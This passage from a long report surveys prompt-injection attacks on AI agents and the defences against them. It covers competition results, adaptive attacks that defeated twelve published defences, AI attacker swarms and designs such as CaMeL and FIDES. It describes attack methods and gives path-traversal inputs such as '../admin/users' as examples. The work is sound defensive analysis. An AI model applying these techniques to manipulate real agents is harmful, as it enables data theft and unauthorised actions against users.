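Dziemian and colleagues call these rates an upper bound for single-turn attacks, because participants could see the agent's conversation and knew exactly which action to cause. A real attacker would have to guess much of this. But the rates average over participants of very different skill, including beginners' failed attempts, and a few participants had a disproportionate influence on the results. A skilled attacker with the same information could do better than the average.

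A more capable model isn't always more robust. In the Arena, the correlation between a model's score on a hard science test and its attack success rate was weak and could have been due to chance. *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark for indirect prompt injection, found that attacks compromised GPT-5 in 26.3% of runs, GPT-5.4 in 12.6%, and the small GPT-5-Nano in 8.4%. A small model may sometimes be safer just because it can't carry out the attacker's instruction, in which case it may also be too weak for the work the developer needs it to do.

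### Attacks that work on more than one model

An attacker can develop an attack on one model and use it against another. After the Arena closed, Dziemian and colleagues took 2,679 attacks that had succeeded and replayed them on all 13 models and two others. The share that worked ranged from 2.5% on Claude Opus 4.5 to 53% on Qwen3 VL 235B.

Attacks that broke strong models transferred best. The 44 attacks in the collection that had broken Opus worked on every other model at rates between 44% and 81%, while none of the attacks that had broken Qwen worked on Opus. The spring competition showed the same pattern. A developer who tests an application only with attacks collected from weak models could therefore get a very reassuring result that is little evidence of how the application would hold up against a strong attacker.

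Some attacks also worked in many situations. One participant wrote 63 texts that differed by only a few words and together succeeded in 21 scenarios and on nine models. An attacker with such a template can reuse it against many applications with little effort.

Other data suggest less transfer. *CounterSteer* (2026) analysed an earlier public challenge in which teams sent attack emails to two models under the same defences. When teams sent the same email to both, attacks that had worked on one model also worked on the other in 44 of 307 cases (14.3%). The teams chose which emails to resend, so this sample, like the Arena's collection of successes, is not random. Transfer rates depend heavily on which attacks, models and defences the researchers include.

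### Twelve defences against attackers who adapt

Developers often test a defence against a fixed set of known attacks. The results can look excellent because the developers designed the defence with those or similar attacks in mind. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 defences against attackers who could change their approach after seeing how the defence responded.

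The automated attacks all worked in a loop, in which the attacker tried a text and used the defended system's response to propose a better one. In one method, a language model rewrote the most promising texts. Another used reinforcement learning to train the attacking model itself on its successes and failures. A third used calculations on the target model's internal values. The researchers also held an online competition in which more than 500 people attacked by hand.

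| What the defence does | Defences | Success rate of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Adds or repeats instructions in the prompt | Spotlighting, Prompt Sandwiching, RPO | Above 95% for all three |
| Trains the model on examples of attacks | Circuit Breakers, StruQ, MetaSecAlign | 96% for MetaSecAlign, 100% for the other two |
| Uses a separate model to detect attacks | Protect AI Detector, PromptGuard, Model Armor, PIGuard | 71% for PIGuard, above 90% for the others |
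| Runs a hidden check that the attacker does not know about | Data Sentinel, MELON | Data Sentinel bypassed in every case; 76% for MELON, or 95% if the attacker knew how it worked |

Most of these defences had first been published with attack success rates near zero. MetaSecAlign's developers, for example, had reported 2% on AgentDojo, a standard set of agent tasks with fixed attacks. When Nasr and colleagues tested Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching against AgentDojo's fixed attacks, as few as 1% succeeded.

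The MELON defense runs the model a second time with a harmless request in place of the user's. If the model makes the same tool call both times, the instruction for that call probably came from the outside content, and MELON raises an alarm. Attackers who knew how MELON works found texts that caused the tool call only in the first run. The automated search found some such texts by chance, even without that knowledge.

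The percentages don't rank the defences, because the researchers followed each defence's original test where they could. RPO and Circuit Breakers also mainly address a different problem, jailbreaks, in which users try to make a model produce content that its developer forbids. Unlike many real attackers, those in the experiment had a large computing budget and, in the tests of separate detectors, could see how confident the detector was about each attempt. The experiment therefore shows that a determined attacker can beat these defences, but not how much it would cost against a live product. Nasr and colleagues still recommend, as one layer of protection, detectors, which stop unsophisticated attacks.

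The results are strong evidence against relying on a prompt, extra training or a detector to recognise every attack. They do not show how well limiting what the agent's tools can do would work, because none of the 12 defences did that.

### Teams of AI attackers

In 2025, people were still better attackers than programs. On a subset of the scenarios and defences, Nasr and colleagues' automated search succeeded in 69% of cases, while the human participants together succeeded in all of them. By autumn 2026, strong models were hard to break with attacks from the competitions. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026), citing Google DeepMind's October safety report on Gemini 4 Argon, reports that recent Gemini models and some Claude models failed on less than 1% of attacks transferred from the Arena.

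The same Google DeepMind researchers then tested whether better attackers could still succeed. They built a swarm of 16 AI agents in eight teams. The agents wrote attacks, read one another's notes, and consulted a list of the best attempts so far. They had up to 320 tries in each of 100 scenarios.

The swarm succeeded if it made the model call a tool unrelated to the user's request. In one scenario, a user books a tutoring session, and the attack has to make the assistant record a blood pressure reading. The researchers chose mostly harmless actions because they wanted to measure whether the model would obey a stranger's instructions. A model that would otherwise obey may refuse to steal data because it recognises theft.

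With Gemini 4 Argon as the attacker, the results were:

| Model under attack | Scenarios broken, out of 100 |
|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Argon | 34 |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 90 |
| Gemini 3.7 Flash | 94 |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 99 |
| Kimi K3 | 99 |
| GLM-5.3 | 99 |
| DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash | 99 |

The attackers also improved with practice. Against Gemini 3.8 Flash, a swarm that began without prepared strategies broke 65 scenarios within 150 tries per scenario. When it could save what had worked in one scenario and use it in the next, it broke 95.

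The results of under 1% and 34% for Google's models can both be right because they come from different kinds of test. The first test replays old attacks, mostly written for other models, while the second creates new ones for the model under attack. The second also ran without the protections that Google normally places around Gemini, and a model may follow a harmless instruction more readily than one to leak a password. The 34% is therefore not an estimate of how often an attacker could steal data from a Gemini product, but it does show that a model's own refusals remain unreliable against a patient attacker, even when old attacks rarely break it.

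### What a low success rate means

Suppose an attack works 1% of the time and the attacker can try it 100 times. If the attempts are independent, the chance that all of them fail is 0.99 multiplied by itself 100 times. The chance of at least one success is then:

```text
1 − 0.99^100 = 1 − 0.366 = 0.634, or about 63%
```

A 1% success rate is high for an attacker who can send thousands of emails, because one success may be enough to steal a key and failed attempts may take almost no money or effort.

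Real attempts are not fully independent. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports success rates of 4.7% after one attempt, 33.6% after ten and 63% after 100 on a Gray Swan benchmark of strong attacks. If each attempt had an independent 4.7% chance of success, the rate would reach 38% after ten attempts and 99% after 100. The slower rise probably means that some scenarios were much harder than others, so extra attempts in the hard ones often failed too. The simple calculation therefore overestimates the success of an attacker who repeats similar attempts in one difficult scenario. It is more accurate for an attacker who can choose among many different targets.

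The opposite problem arises when a test finds no successes at all. A model that refuses ten attacks out of ten, as two models did in every TicketOracle scenario, has an observed success rate of 0%. To find how high the true rate could still be, one can look for the rate at which ten failures in a row would happen only 5% of the time:

```text
 10 trials: 1 − 0.05^(1/10)  = 0.259, or about 26%
300 trials: 1 − 0.05^(1/300) = 0.010, or about 1%
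```

If a model refuses an attack in all ten trials, a tester can conclude with 95% confidence only that the attack works no more than about one time in four. To show that the rate is no higher than about 1%, the tester needs 300 independent trials without a success. When no attack succeeds, the upper limit is roughly three divided by the number of trials, unless that number is very small.

The calculation applies only to the attacker in the test. When Kurakin and colleagues used Gemini 3.6 Flash to attack Gemini 4 Argon, the attacks failed in all 100 scenarios within 150 tries. By the same formula, the upper limit for that attacker would be about 3% of such scenarios. But when Gemini 4 Argon was the attacker, it succeeded in 13 scenarios within 150 tries and in 34 within 320. More trials with the weaker attacker would have lowered the upper limit without revealing that a stronger attacker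 could succeed.

### Why the companies' figures cannot be compared

AI companies publish prompt-injection results in system cards, documents that describe a model's tests and risks. The table combines figures from several tests that the companies ran or reported in 2026.

| Model | Test | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Recent Gemini models | Attacks transferred from the Arena | Under 1% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Direct attacks from OpenAI's automated attacker | About 0.05% |
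| GPT-5.6 Sol | Indirect attacks in OpenAI's own tests | 3.77% on average |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | One attempt on a coding agent, without and with safeguards | 7.03% and 2.09% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | One attempt on an agent that operates a graphical interface, without safeguards | 17.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Up to 200 attempts on the same kind of agent, without and with safeguards | 78.6% and 57.1% |

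The OpenAI figures come from TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, and the figures for the two Claude models come from VentureBeat. Anthropic and OpenAI have since released newer models, Claude Fable 5.2 and GPT-6.2 Astra, so the table is more useful for showing how companies measure the problem than for choosing a model. Anthropic also reported that Claude Mythos 5, which came between Opus 4.8 and Fable 5.2, achieved the best result to that point on a Gray Swan prompt-injection benchmark.

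The lowest rates for GPT-5.6 Sol (0.05%) and Claude Opus 4.8 (7.03%) don't show which model is safer, because the first is for instructions that a user types and the second is for instructions planted in material that a coding agent reads. OpenAI's 3.77% is the nearest comparison to Claude's rate, but it covers different tasks and different attackers. Kurakin and colleagues also note that OpenAI's automated attacker, GPT-Red, helps train the company's models to resist attacks. A low rate against GPT-Red may partly reflect that training.

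The choice of tasks can change the result more than the choice of model. According to VentureBeat, Opus 4.6 withstood all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment, even without safeguards. *Adaptive Adversaries* (2026) tested one model, gpt-oss-20b, against one standard attacker in 21 scenarios, with 50 trials of each. The attacker succeeded more than 70% of the time in seven scenarios and less than 20% of the time in nine, including three in which it never succeeded. A tester could report almost any attack success rate for this model by choosing among these scenarios.

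A fair comparison would use the same scenarios, attackers, number of attempts and safeguards for every model. The competitions come closer to this than the system cards do. In the Arena, participants did not know which model they were attacking, and most models faced a similar number of people.

### Flaws that a model test cannot find

The competitions used simulated tools. An agent's request to read a record might go to another language model, which invented a plausible response. This is a safe way to test whether a model follows a planted instruction, but the simulation has no real parser, database or shell to attack. It could not have revealed the flaw in vLLM's parser, which ran code while reading a tool call, or the OpenClaw attack, which didn't need a model.

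A model test can also make an application look less safe than it is. If the model produces a forbidden tool call, the test counts the attack as successful, even though the real executor might check the call and block it. *AgentTriage* (Ying, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) points out that an agent's final reply does not reveal what its tools did. An agent may write that it has saved a file when the call failed, or omit an action that succeeded. The paper's program records each tool call and its result, and gives no conclusion when necessary evidence is missing. It got the whole diagnosis right, with evidence for each part, in 86% of 120 test cases.

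Fuzzing is one way to test the real application. A fuzzer is a program that sends many inputs to other software and uses the results to choose further inputs. An ordinary fuzzer might send random characters, but an agent would usually reply that it did not understand them, so a fuzzer for agents has to write requests that make the agent use the right tool.

AgentFuzz (USENIX Security 2025), like LLMSmith, works backwards from dangerous functions in the source code. A language model then writes requests for the features that could lead to those functions. AgentFuzz runs the agent on these requests, measures how close each one comes to the dangerous function, and rewrites the most promising ones. It found 34 previously unreported flaws in 20 open-source agent applications.

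ChainFuzzer (2026) looks for flaws that appear only when an agent uses several tools in a row. For example, one tool might save text from a web page to a file, and another might read the file and put its contents into a command. Each tool may pass a test on its own, because the first never runs anything and the second reads only local files. Together, they could let the web page's author run shell commands. ChainFuzzer searches for tools whose output can become another tool's input, writes a request that makes the agent use them in that order, and checks whether harmful text reaches the last tool. In tests on 20 popular agent applications, most of the confirmed flaws needed more than one tool.

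Fuzzers of this kind need the application's source code, and they find only the types of harm they are programmed to detect. They can detect a command that runs when it shouldn't, but they miss a chatbot showing one customer another's order unless the tester has specified who may see what. Competitions are also beginning to cover more of the application. Gray Swan has announced a three-week bug bounty for attacks on complete agent products, according to the *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026) from the AI company Reflection, one of the bounty's sponsors.

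### When has a team tested enough?

Red-teaming has no agreed scope or stopping point. "We red-teamed the product" may mean that a few employees typed attacks into a chat window for an afternoon, or that many agents attacked every tool for a week. The studies described here also define success differently. Successes in the spring 2025 competition included prohibited content such as scam messages, the Arena usually required the agent to hide what it had done, and Kurakin and colleagues counted harmless tool calls.

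The number of attempts matters just as much. In Gray Swan's benchmark, a company that stopped after one attempt per scenario would have reported an attack success rate of 4.7% for Claude Opus 4.5, and one that stopped after 100 would have reported 63%. A company can therefore get a better result by stopping early, and outsiders cannot tell unless they know how many attempts it made.

Nasr and colleagues accept that testing can never prove a defence secure. They think the tester's job is to try as hard as possible to break it and fail, so the amount of effort is part of the evidence. They advise developers to attack their own defences manually and make it easy for others to do the same. This makes a weak test easier to recognise, though it provides no rule for when to stop testing.

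Another answer is to fix the maximum number of tries in advance and publish the results at several points, as Kurakin and colleagues did for 150 and 320 tries. Any maximum is arbitrary, but if everyone uses the same one, the results show which of two models is harder to break and whether a new version is better than the last.

*Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition*, from the US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), defends the competitions on similar grounds. They show large differences between models, which can help a company choose one, and they produce new attacks for later tests. CAISI also expects testing to continue indefinitely, because attackers keep changing their methods. Gray Swan has accordingly repeated the Arena several times in 2026. On this view, security testing normally has no stopping rule, and it is a mistake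 to treat one round of tests as proof that a model is secure.

These replies are convincing for comparisons between models, but a developer deciding whether to release an application needs something more specific. The developer can at least set the scope by listing the application's tools, the sources of text that outsiders can influence, and the actions that must never happen. A reasonable minimum is then to test every route from those sources to those actions, with a stated number of attempts for each. The acceptable risk depends on the tool. For a shell with access to the company's keys, even one successful attack in 100 attempts is far too many, and further refusal training is unlikely to bring the rate to zero.

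## Which interface designs limit what an injected prompt can do?

A developer who cannot count on the model to refuse has to limit what its tool calls can do. Most of the useful practices follow from treating every parameter the model can influence as if an attacker had written it. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian consider checks in the application's own code the most important defence because they work whether or not the model complies.

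The model chooses which tools to call, in what order and how many times, and it influences the values in each call. It may also write text that a tool saves for later. It cannot influence the customer number in a login session.

To apply the rule, a developer can identify the most damaging value each parameter accepts. For TicketOracle's `fetch_event_data`, it is the most damaging address the server can reach. For a tool that accepts a whole SQL query, it is the most damaging query the database account is allowed to run. If that value is unacceptable, the developer has to restrict what the parameter accepts.

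### Redesigning the concert assistant

TicketOracle's customers only ask about concerts, so its tool has no need to accept addresses. The first change is to let the model name an event and have the application find the address:

```python
def get_event(event_name):
    event = events_on_sale.get(event_name)
    if event is None:
        return {"error": "No such event"}
    response = requests.get(event.address, allow_redirects=False, timeout=5)
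    return response.json()
```

The model can still supply any text, but text that matches no event produces an error. The tool takes the address from the application's own list and does not follow redirects, which could send the request elsewhere. An attacker can therefore no longer direct the tool to the administrative API. Port probing, reading user records, deleting a record and the blind request all stop working, whichever model the site uses.

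If the application builds the URL by appending an unchecked event name to a fixed prefix, part of the problem returns, because a name containing `../` might lead to another page on the same server. An event number is harder to abuse this way because the schema can require an integer.

Some tools, such as one that summarises web pages, have to accept addresses, so they need more checks. The application should convert each address to a standard form, because the same address can be written in several ways, and then reject redirects, unusual protocols and anything on the internal network.

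**Reviews should be separate from the facts.** A customer who asks for a price needs the price, venue and date, so `get_event` should return only those. A planted review then doesn't reach the model when someone asks what a ticket costs, but it still does when someone asks what people thought of the concert. The review can no longer get the model to access the user records, but it can still put a false claim or a malicious link in the reply. The site can prevent this too by displaying the reviews itself, next to the model's answer, but then the model can't summarize them.

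The separation also helps against attacks that contain no instruction. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) describes attacks in which a model treats untrusted data as trusted because it accepts an inexact copy of the delimiters between them. On the concert site, a review could imitate the end of the review field and add a false price. A JSON parser would keep the whole text inside the review, but a model might not. A filter that looks for instructions could miss the false price because it isn't an instruction.

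**The administrative API itself needs protection.** The API still accepts any request from the same machine, so a flaw in another program there could expose the user records. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend that administrative services check who is calling instead of relying on their own position in the network for security. The API should also stop deleting records in response to GET requests. After these changes, a request to the API fails without an administrator's credentials, though an attacker who steals those credentials could still use it.

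Network rules can **deny outbound traffic by default** and allow only the destinations the application needs. In the experiment, TicketOracle's event pages were at a private network address, so blocking all private addresses would have broken the assistant. The rule has to permit that one service and block the rest.

This removes the network route to internal services even if someone later adds a badly designed tool. Data may still leak through allowed destinations that pass it on, as Microsoft Teams and Bing did in the Copilot attacks. It also doesn't cover the customer's browser, so the chat page has to block outside images separately.

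Suppose the site then adds order look-ups, ticket purchases and free-form questions about concerts. Each feature gives an injected prompt something new to misuse:

| Feature | Practice | What it prevents | What an attacker can still do |
|---|---|---|---|
| Order look-ups | Check permission as the logged-in customer | Reading other customers' orders | Expose the victim's own orders through text planted in the victim's session |
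| Questions answered with SQL | Use a database account that can only read public event data | Changing records or reading the users table | Run slow queries |
| Ticket purchases | Limit the quantity, and calculate the price in the application | Buying 500 tickets or setting a price of zero | Buy an unwanted ticket within the limits |
| Payments | Add the payment key after the model has written the call | Copying the key into a reply or a web address | Use the key's permissions through the payment tool |

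For the SQL feature, the developer can create a view, a saved query that works like a table, and give the assistant's account access to nothing else:

```sql
create view public_events as
  select name, venue, event_date, price from events where on_sale;

grant select on public_events to ticket_assistant;
```

The database enforces the restricted account's permissions on every query, however the model words it. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian also suggest parsing each query and rejecting destructive operations. Parsing gives earlier warning, but a mistake in the parser would matter much more without the restricted account.

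To keep the payment key away from the model, developers must leave it out of the system prompt and tool results. For example, an error message that repeats the whole failed request could put the key in the model's context.

If the assistant has a memory, the tool that writes to it needs protection too. In a scenario that Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian constructed, a malicious web page makes the victim's logged-in browser save a false payment address in an assistant's memory. The model later gives the user this address as genuine, even though nobody sent it a malicious instruction.

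The purchase tool can still buy an unwanted ticket, because a purchase within the limits from the customer's own account passes every check in the table. To prevent this, the system has to determine whether the customer or a planted review caused the purchase.

### Keeping untrusted text away from the planner

A model cannot reliably keep instructions and data apart, so the software around it has to separate them, as *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) argues.

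Willison proposed one way to do this in 2023, the dual-LLM pattern. It uses two models and an ordinary program, the orchestrator, that passes data between them. Suppose a customer asks the concert assistant to summarise the reviews of a concert and email the summary to a friend:

1. The privileged model, which can call tools, sees the customer's request and asks for the reviews.
2. The orchestrator stores the reviews under a name, such as `$REVIEWS`, and gives the privileged model only that name.
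3. The quarantined model, which has no tools, reads the reviews and writes a summary. The orchestrator stores it as `$SUMMARY`.
4. The privileged model calls the email tool with the friend's address and `$SUMMARY`. The orchestrator inserts the actual text as it sends the email.

An instruction in a review reaches only the quarantined model. It can corrupt the summary, but it cannot add a tool call or change the recipient, however persuasive it is, because the model that chooses the actions never receives the review.

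The guarantee assumes that the customer's request is trustworthy. If the customer pastes in text from a malicious website, the privileged model reads the attacker's words directly. The orchestrator must also never show the privileged model free text from the quarantined one. Willison proposed the design without benchmark results.

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) lists this pattern as one of six. All six follow the principle that untrusted text must not be able to trigger a consequential action once a model has read it.

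| Pattern | How it works | What an attacker can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees their results | Trigger the wrong action from the list by typing a misleading request |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its list of tool calls before it reads outside data | Change what those calls contain |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and gives a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Get their own document misjudged |
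| Dual LLM | The model with tools handles untrusted text only by name | Corrupt the text behind the name |
| Code, then execute | The model writes a program that calls tools and quarantined models | Corrupt the data that the program handles |
| Context minimisation | The application removes the user's prompt before the model writes its reply | Influence the first step, such as a database search |

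A fixed plan offers less protection when its tools are broad, so the developer also needs to keep the tools narrow. In one of the paper's examples, an assistant that tidies files commits to using only the commands for finding and moving them. A planted instruction could still make it find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply the patterns to ten kinds of application but do not measure attack success rates. They doubt that a general-purpose agent can be made reliably secure with current models, and recommend building agents for specific jobs. How much usefulness an agent loses under these patterns depends heavily on the job. A customer service bot loses little by choosing from a list of actions, such as sending a link to the last order or opening the password settings. Their safest design for a coding agent converts outside documentation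 into a rigid description of functions, for instance with names of at most 30 characters, so the agent never sees the explanations and examples that programmers rely on.

### CaMeL: checking where each value came from

The dual-LLM pattern has a gap when untrusted text supplies an important value. Suppose a customer asks the assistant to send a ticket to the address in Anna's latest message. The privileged model could write this program:

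```python
message = latest_message(sender="Anna")
address = quarantined_llm("Find the email address", message)
ticket = get_ticket(order="latest")
send_email(to=address, attachment=ticket)
```

An attacker who got text into Anna's message could not add a fifth line, but could replace the address and receive the ticket.

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind published in 2025, addresses this gap. A privileged model writes a program from the user's request, and CaMeL's interpreter runs it. The interpreter records where each value came from and who may read it, and passes these records on to anything calculated from the value. As *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains, security policies are Python functions that inspect each tool call and its arguments, then allow or deny the call and give a reason. In the ticket example, a policy could block the email because the address came from a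 message, or have the customer confirm it.

*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) reports CaMeL's results on the AgentDojo benchmark. CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and no attack covered by its threat model succeeded. CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens as the undefended agent.

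CaMeL's guarantee depends on correct policies and correct records of where data came from. It covers only actions, so a poisoned document can still produce a misleading summary, which the CaMeL paper explicitly leaves out of scope. The paper also describes ways to leak data indirectly. For example, if a program makes a visible request only when a secret has a certain value, an observer can learn something about the secret without receiving it. An attacker can also cause an error that stops the program and learn something from which later actions don't happen.

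Two papers from autumn 2026 build on CaMeL. *CaMeLoT* adds temporal logic, a formal way of stating rules about the order of events, so that software can check a plan before running it. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* extends CaMeL to several agents that work together. The paper's tests also showed that CaMeL needs a description of what each tool returns, because its planner has to write the code that handles a tool's output before seeing any output. AgentDojo's standard tool descriptions lacked this information, so the researchers had to add it. Ordinary agents can manage without it, but a developer who might adopt a design like CaMeL later should include it from the start.

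### FIDES: labels that travel with the data

CaMeL's plan cannot depend on what the tools return. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a system developed at Microsoft. FIDES lets an agent adjust its plan as it works, but restricts what the agent can do after reading untrusted text.

FIDES gives every piece of data two labels, one for whether it is trusted and one for who may read it. When the agent combines data, the result is untrusted if any source was untrusted, and only people who could read every source may read it.

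Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example with no attacker. Alex's assistant reads an email from Priya containing unreleased sales figures, and another from Marco, who is curious about them. Alex and Priya are allowed to read the first email, and Alex and Marco are allowed to read the second. Because Alex is the only person allowed to read both, only Alex may read a reply based on them, and the assistant cannot send it to Marco without asking.

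Before each tool call, ordinary code checks the labels against a policy. One basic policy permits a consequential action, such as a bank transfer, only if no untrusted data influenced it. Another permits the agent to send data only to people authorized to read it.

An agent that read every email directly would soon be able to do very little, because its whole context would become untrusted. FIDES therefore hides untrusted results behind names, as the dual-LLM pattern does, and lets a quarantined model answer restricted questions about them. If the user wants any meeting request in the inbox added to the calendar, the agent works like this:

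1. It fetches the emails without reading them.
2. The quarantined model answers yes or no to the question of whether they contain a meeting request.
3. The planner reads this one-word answer.
4. If the answer is yes, the quarantined model extracts the date, time and participants.
5. The planner passes these details to the calendar tool, still without reading them.

A malicious email could cause a false calendar entry, but it could not make the agent forward the inbox, because a yes-or-no answer cannot contain an instruction. The policy needs an exception for such answers, since they come from untrusted text.

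Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, using an attack that names the agent's tools. They counted 152 real successes against an ordinary agent and none against FIDES with its policies switched on. Without the policies, 21 attacks succeeded, because the planner could open untrusted text and carry on as normal. The next table shows how many tasks the agents completed when nobody was attacking them:

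| Type of task | Ordinary agent | Ordinary agent with label checks | FIDES with label checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack messages | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Hiding untrusted text recovers part of the task completion lost to the label checks, except in the travel tasks, where GPT-4o struggled with the hidden values. FIDES did better on those tasks with a stronger model, OpenAI's o1, completing 68% of them. Other failures were intentional, since many banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the policy forbids.

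FIDES guarantees that data does not flow directly to the wrong place, but, like CaMeL, it can leak information through the agent's choice of actions. It also doesn't prevent bad judgement. In one banking task, the agent had to change the user's password if it found a suspicious transaction. It saw the amounts and dates but not the untrusted descriptions, decided that a large payment was suspicious, and changed the password. This violated no policy because the agent had read only trusted data.

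### Labels in Microsoft's products

Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (May 2026) announced FIDES as an experimental feature of Agent Framework, the company's software for building agents. In its example, an agent that sorts GitHub issues reads a planted instruction to post the contents of a secret file. The agent can open the file, but its contents are labelled private and the commenting tool accepts only public data, so the framework blocks the comment and can ask a person what to do.

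Microsoft has also worked with GitHub to add optional labels to GitHub's MCP server, and an experimental setting in the Copilot command-line program enforces policies on some of that server's tools. The labels mark content from public repositories as public and untrusted, and content from private repositories as private and trusted. If an employee copied an outsider's bug report into a private repository, the report would therefore be labeled as trusted.

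Forgotten labels are a larger risk. In Agent Framework, a tool without a label counts as trusted and public, so a developer who overlooks one data source loses the protection without any warning. Microsoft has asked users whether unlabelled data should count as untrusted by default. That would be safer but would probably break many agents as soon as developers switched it on. Microsoft's documentation makes the application's developer responsible for validating inputs and configuring tools.

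### Meta's Rule of Two

Meta published a simpler rule in October 2025. Within one session, an agent should have at most two of these properties:

- It processes untrusted input.
- It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- It can change something or communicate with the outside.

If a task needs all three, a person or another reliable check has to supervise the agent. The rule resembles Willison's lethal trifecta, but its third property includes changes as well as outside communication. It therefore also covers the job-site attack that replaced a user's email address without sending any data out.

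The Rule of Two is a planning rule, with no benchmark result and no mechanism that enforces it. Two properties can also be enough to cause harm, as in TicketOracle's planted-review attack, which used only the first two. The rule works best as a first check on a design, before the developer looks at who may see what each tool returns.

### What does the loss of flexibility cost?

An agent is useful partly because it can change its plan when it finds something unexpected, and strict designs limit this. Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) argue in *AgentDyn* that the usual tests don't reveal this problem. Only six of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan after seeing new information, so a defence can score well by sticking to the original plan. AgentDojo also contains few helpful instructions from third parties, such as a checkout page that tells the customer to log in first, so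 a defence loses little by ignoring all third-party instructions.

Li and colleagues built 60 tasks that require new plans and contain at least one helpful outside instruction. The tasks average about seven steps, twice as many as AgentDojo's. Designs that rely on an initial plan, including CaMeL, completed far fewer of these tasks than an undefended agent. Progent, which checks each tool call against a list of permissions, also did much worse because the right permissions are hard to choose when there are many tools. The researchers tested ten defences and concluded that almost all were either too weak or too restrictive for real use.

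Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, accept that strict designs can cut task completion on AgentDojo by up to 30%, but consider the usual comparison unfair. The score for a strict design counts only tasks it finishes without help. The undefended agent may do anything without asking, whereas many real products require a person to approve its important actions. They therefore measured how many tasks each agent could finish without a single approval:

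| Agent, using OpenAI's o3-mini | Tasks finished without approval |
|---|---|
| Ordinary agent that asks before every consequential action | 24.3% |
| The same agent, asking only when a label check fails | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 50.1% |
| PRUDENTIA | 59.1% |

PRUDENTIA, the successor to FIDES, gives the planner the policies so it can avoid actions that would need approval. It can also prompt the user to vouch for a piece of text. If a harmless email lists ten actions, the user can approve the email once instead of approving each action. With o4-mini, PRUDENTIA needed about half as many approvals as FIDES but completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% versus 75.7%).

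On WASP, a benchmark for agents that use websites, attacks diverted an ordinary agent in 15% to 61% of cases, depending on the model and the site. None diverted PRUDENTIA, which needed no approvals and completed at least as many tasks. But the test's only user tasks were posting a comment and voting for a post, which the agent can do without reading untrusted text.

Both groups have a point, depending on the task. If the user's request already determines what should happen, a strict design has few drawbacks. But if the agent has to find out what to do from an email or a web page, it needs text that may also contain the attack. Narisetty and colleagues consider such tasks the deepest open problem for these designs, since the usual answer is to ask the user, who may approve without looking closely.

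Restricting the interface of a narrow product can remove almost no useful functionality. The concert assistant, for example, lost the ability to open arbitrary web addresses, which no customer had asked for.

### Attackers who study the rules

CaMeL and FIDES achieved their perfect AgentDojo scores against fixed attacks. The 12 defences that Nasr and colleagues studied had also looked strong in that kind of test. Narisetty and colleagues tried an adaptive attack on Progent, which uses a language model to write its rules and ordinary code to enforce them. The attack presented a malicious action as a necessary step that had already been approved, so that the model would add it to the permitted actions.

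| Test | Attack success rate per test case |
|---|---|
| No defence, standard attack | 25.8% |
| Progent, standard attack | 4.2% |
| Progent, adaptive attack | 2.6% |

This evidence is encouraging but weak. The researchers tried one handwritten attack on a small model, Qwen2.5-7B, and the attack's mild wording may have made the agent itself less likely to obey. Progent also reduced the share of tasks completed under the standard attack from 45.2% to 27.1% and required about 15 times as many model calls.

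These designs should still resist attacks better than a detector. An attacker can beat a detector by finding wording it misclassifies, but beating a fixed rule requires finding a flaw in the rule, getting data mislabeled, or doing harm with actions the rule permits. These are ordinary security problems that a developer can look for in the code.

### What official guidance adds

OWASP, a non-profit that publishes security advice for developers, includes "excessive agency" as a separate risk in its 2025 list for LLM applications. It divides the risk into too many functions, too many permissions and too much independence. Most of its recommendations match the practices in the concert example. It also suggests limiting how often an agent can call its tools. This gives people time to notice harmful calls before there are hundreds, though it doesn't prevent individual ones.

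The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) advises designers to assume that prompt injection is possible wherever a model reads untrusted input. Its 2025 report on attacks against machine learning suggests using several models with different permissions, or letting a model reach untrusted data only through a well-defined interface, and the dual-LLM pattern does both.

David C's advice for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre puts more weight on logging tool calls and paying particular attention to failed ones, because an attacker may need several attempts to get an attack right. Such failures stand out in a narrow interface because, for example, a concert customer has no reason to ask for an event called `../admin/users`.

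In *Agentao*, Jin, Jiao and Tong (2026) build logging into the software that runs an agent. The model proposes an action, the host application decides whether to permit it, and the software logs both steps so that someone can replay them later. They claim no formal guarantee of safety, but after an incident the developer can at least use the log to identify which call caused the damage.

David C also accepts that some risk will remain after all this work. He writes that a system that cannot tolerate that risk may not be a good use for an LLM. For example, a bank could still let a model explain its transfer form but leave the transfer to the customer.

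## What do sandboxes and human approval add when the system must run code?

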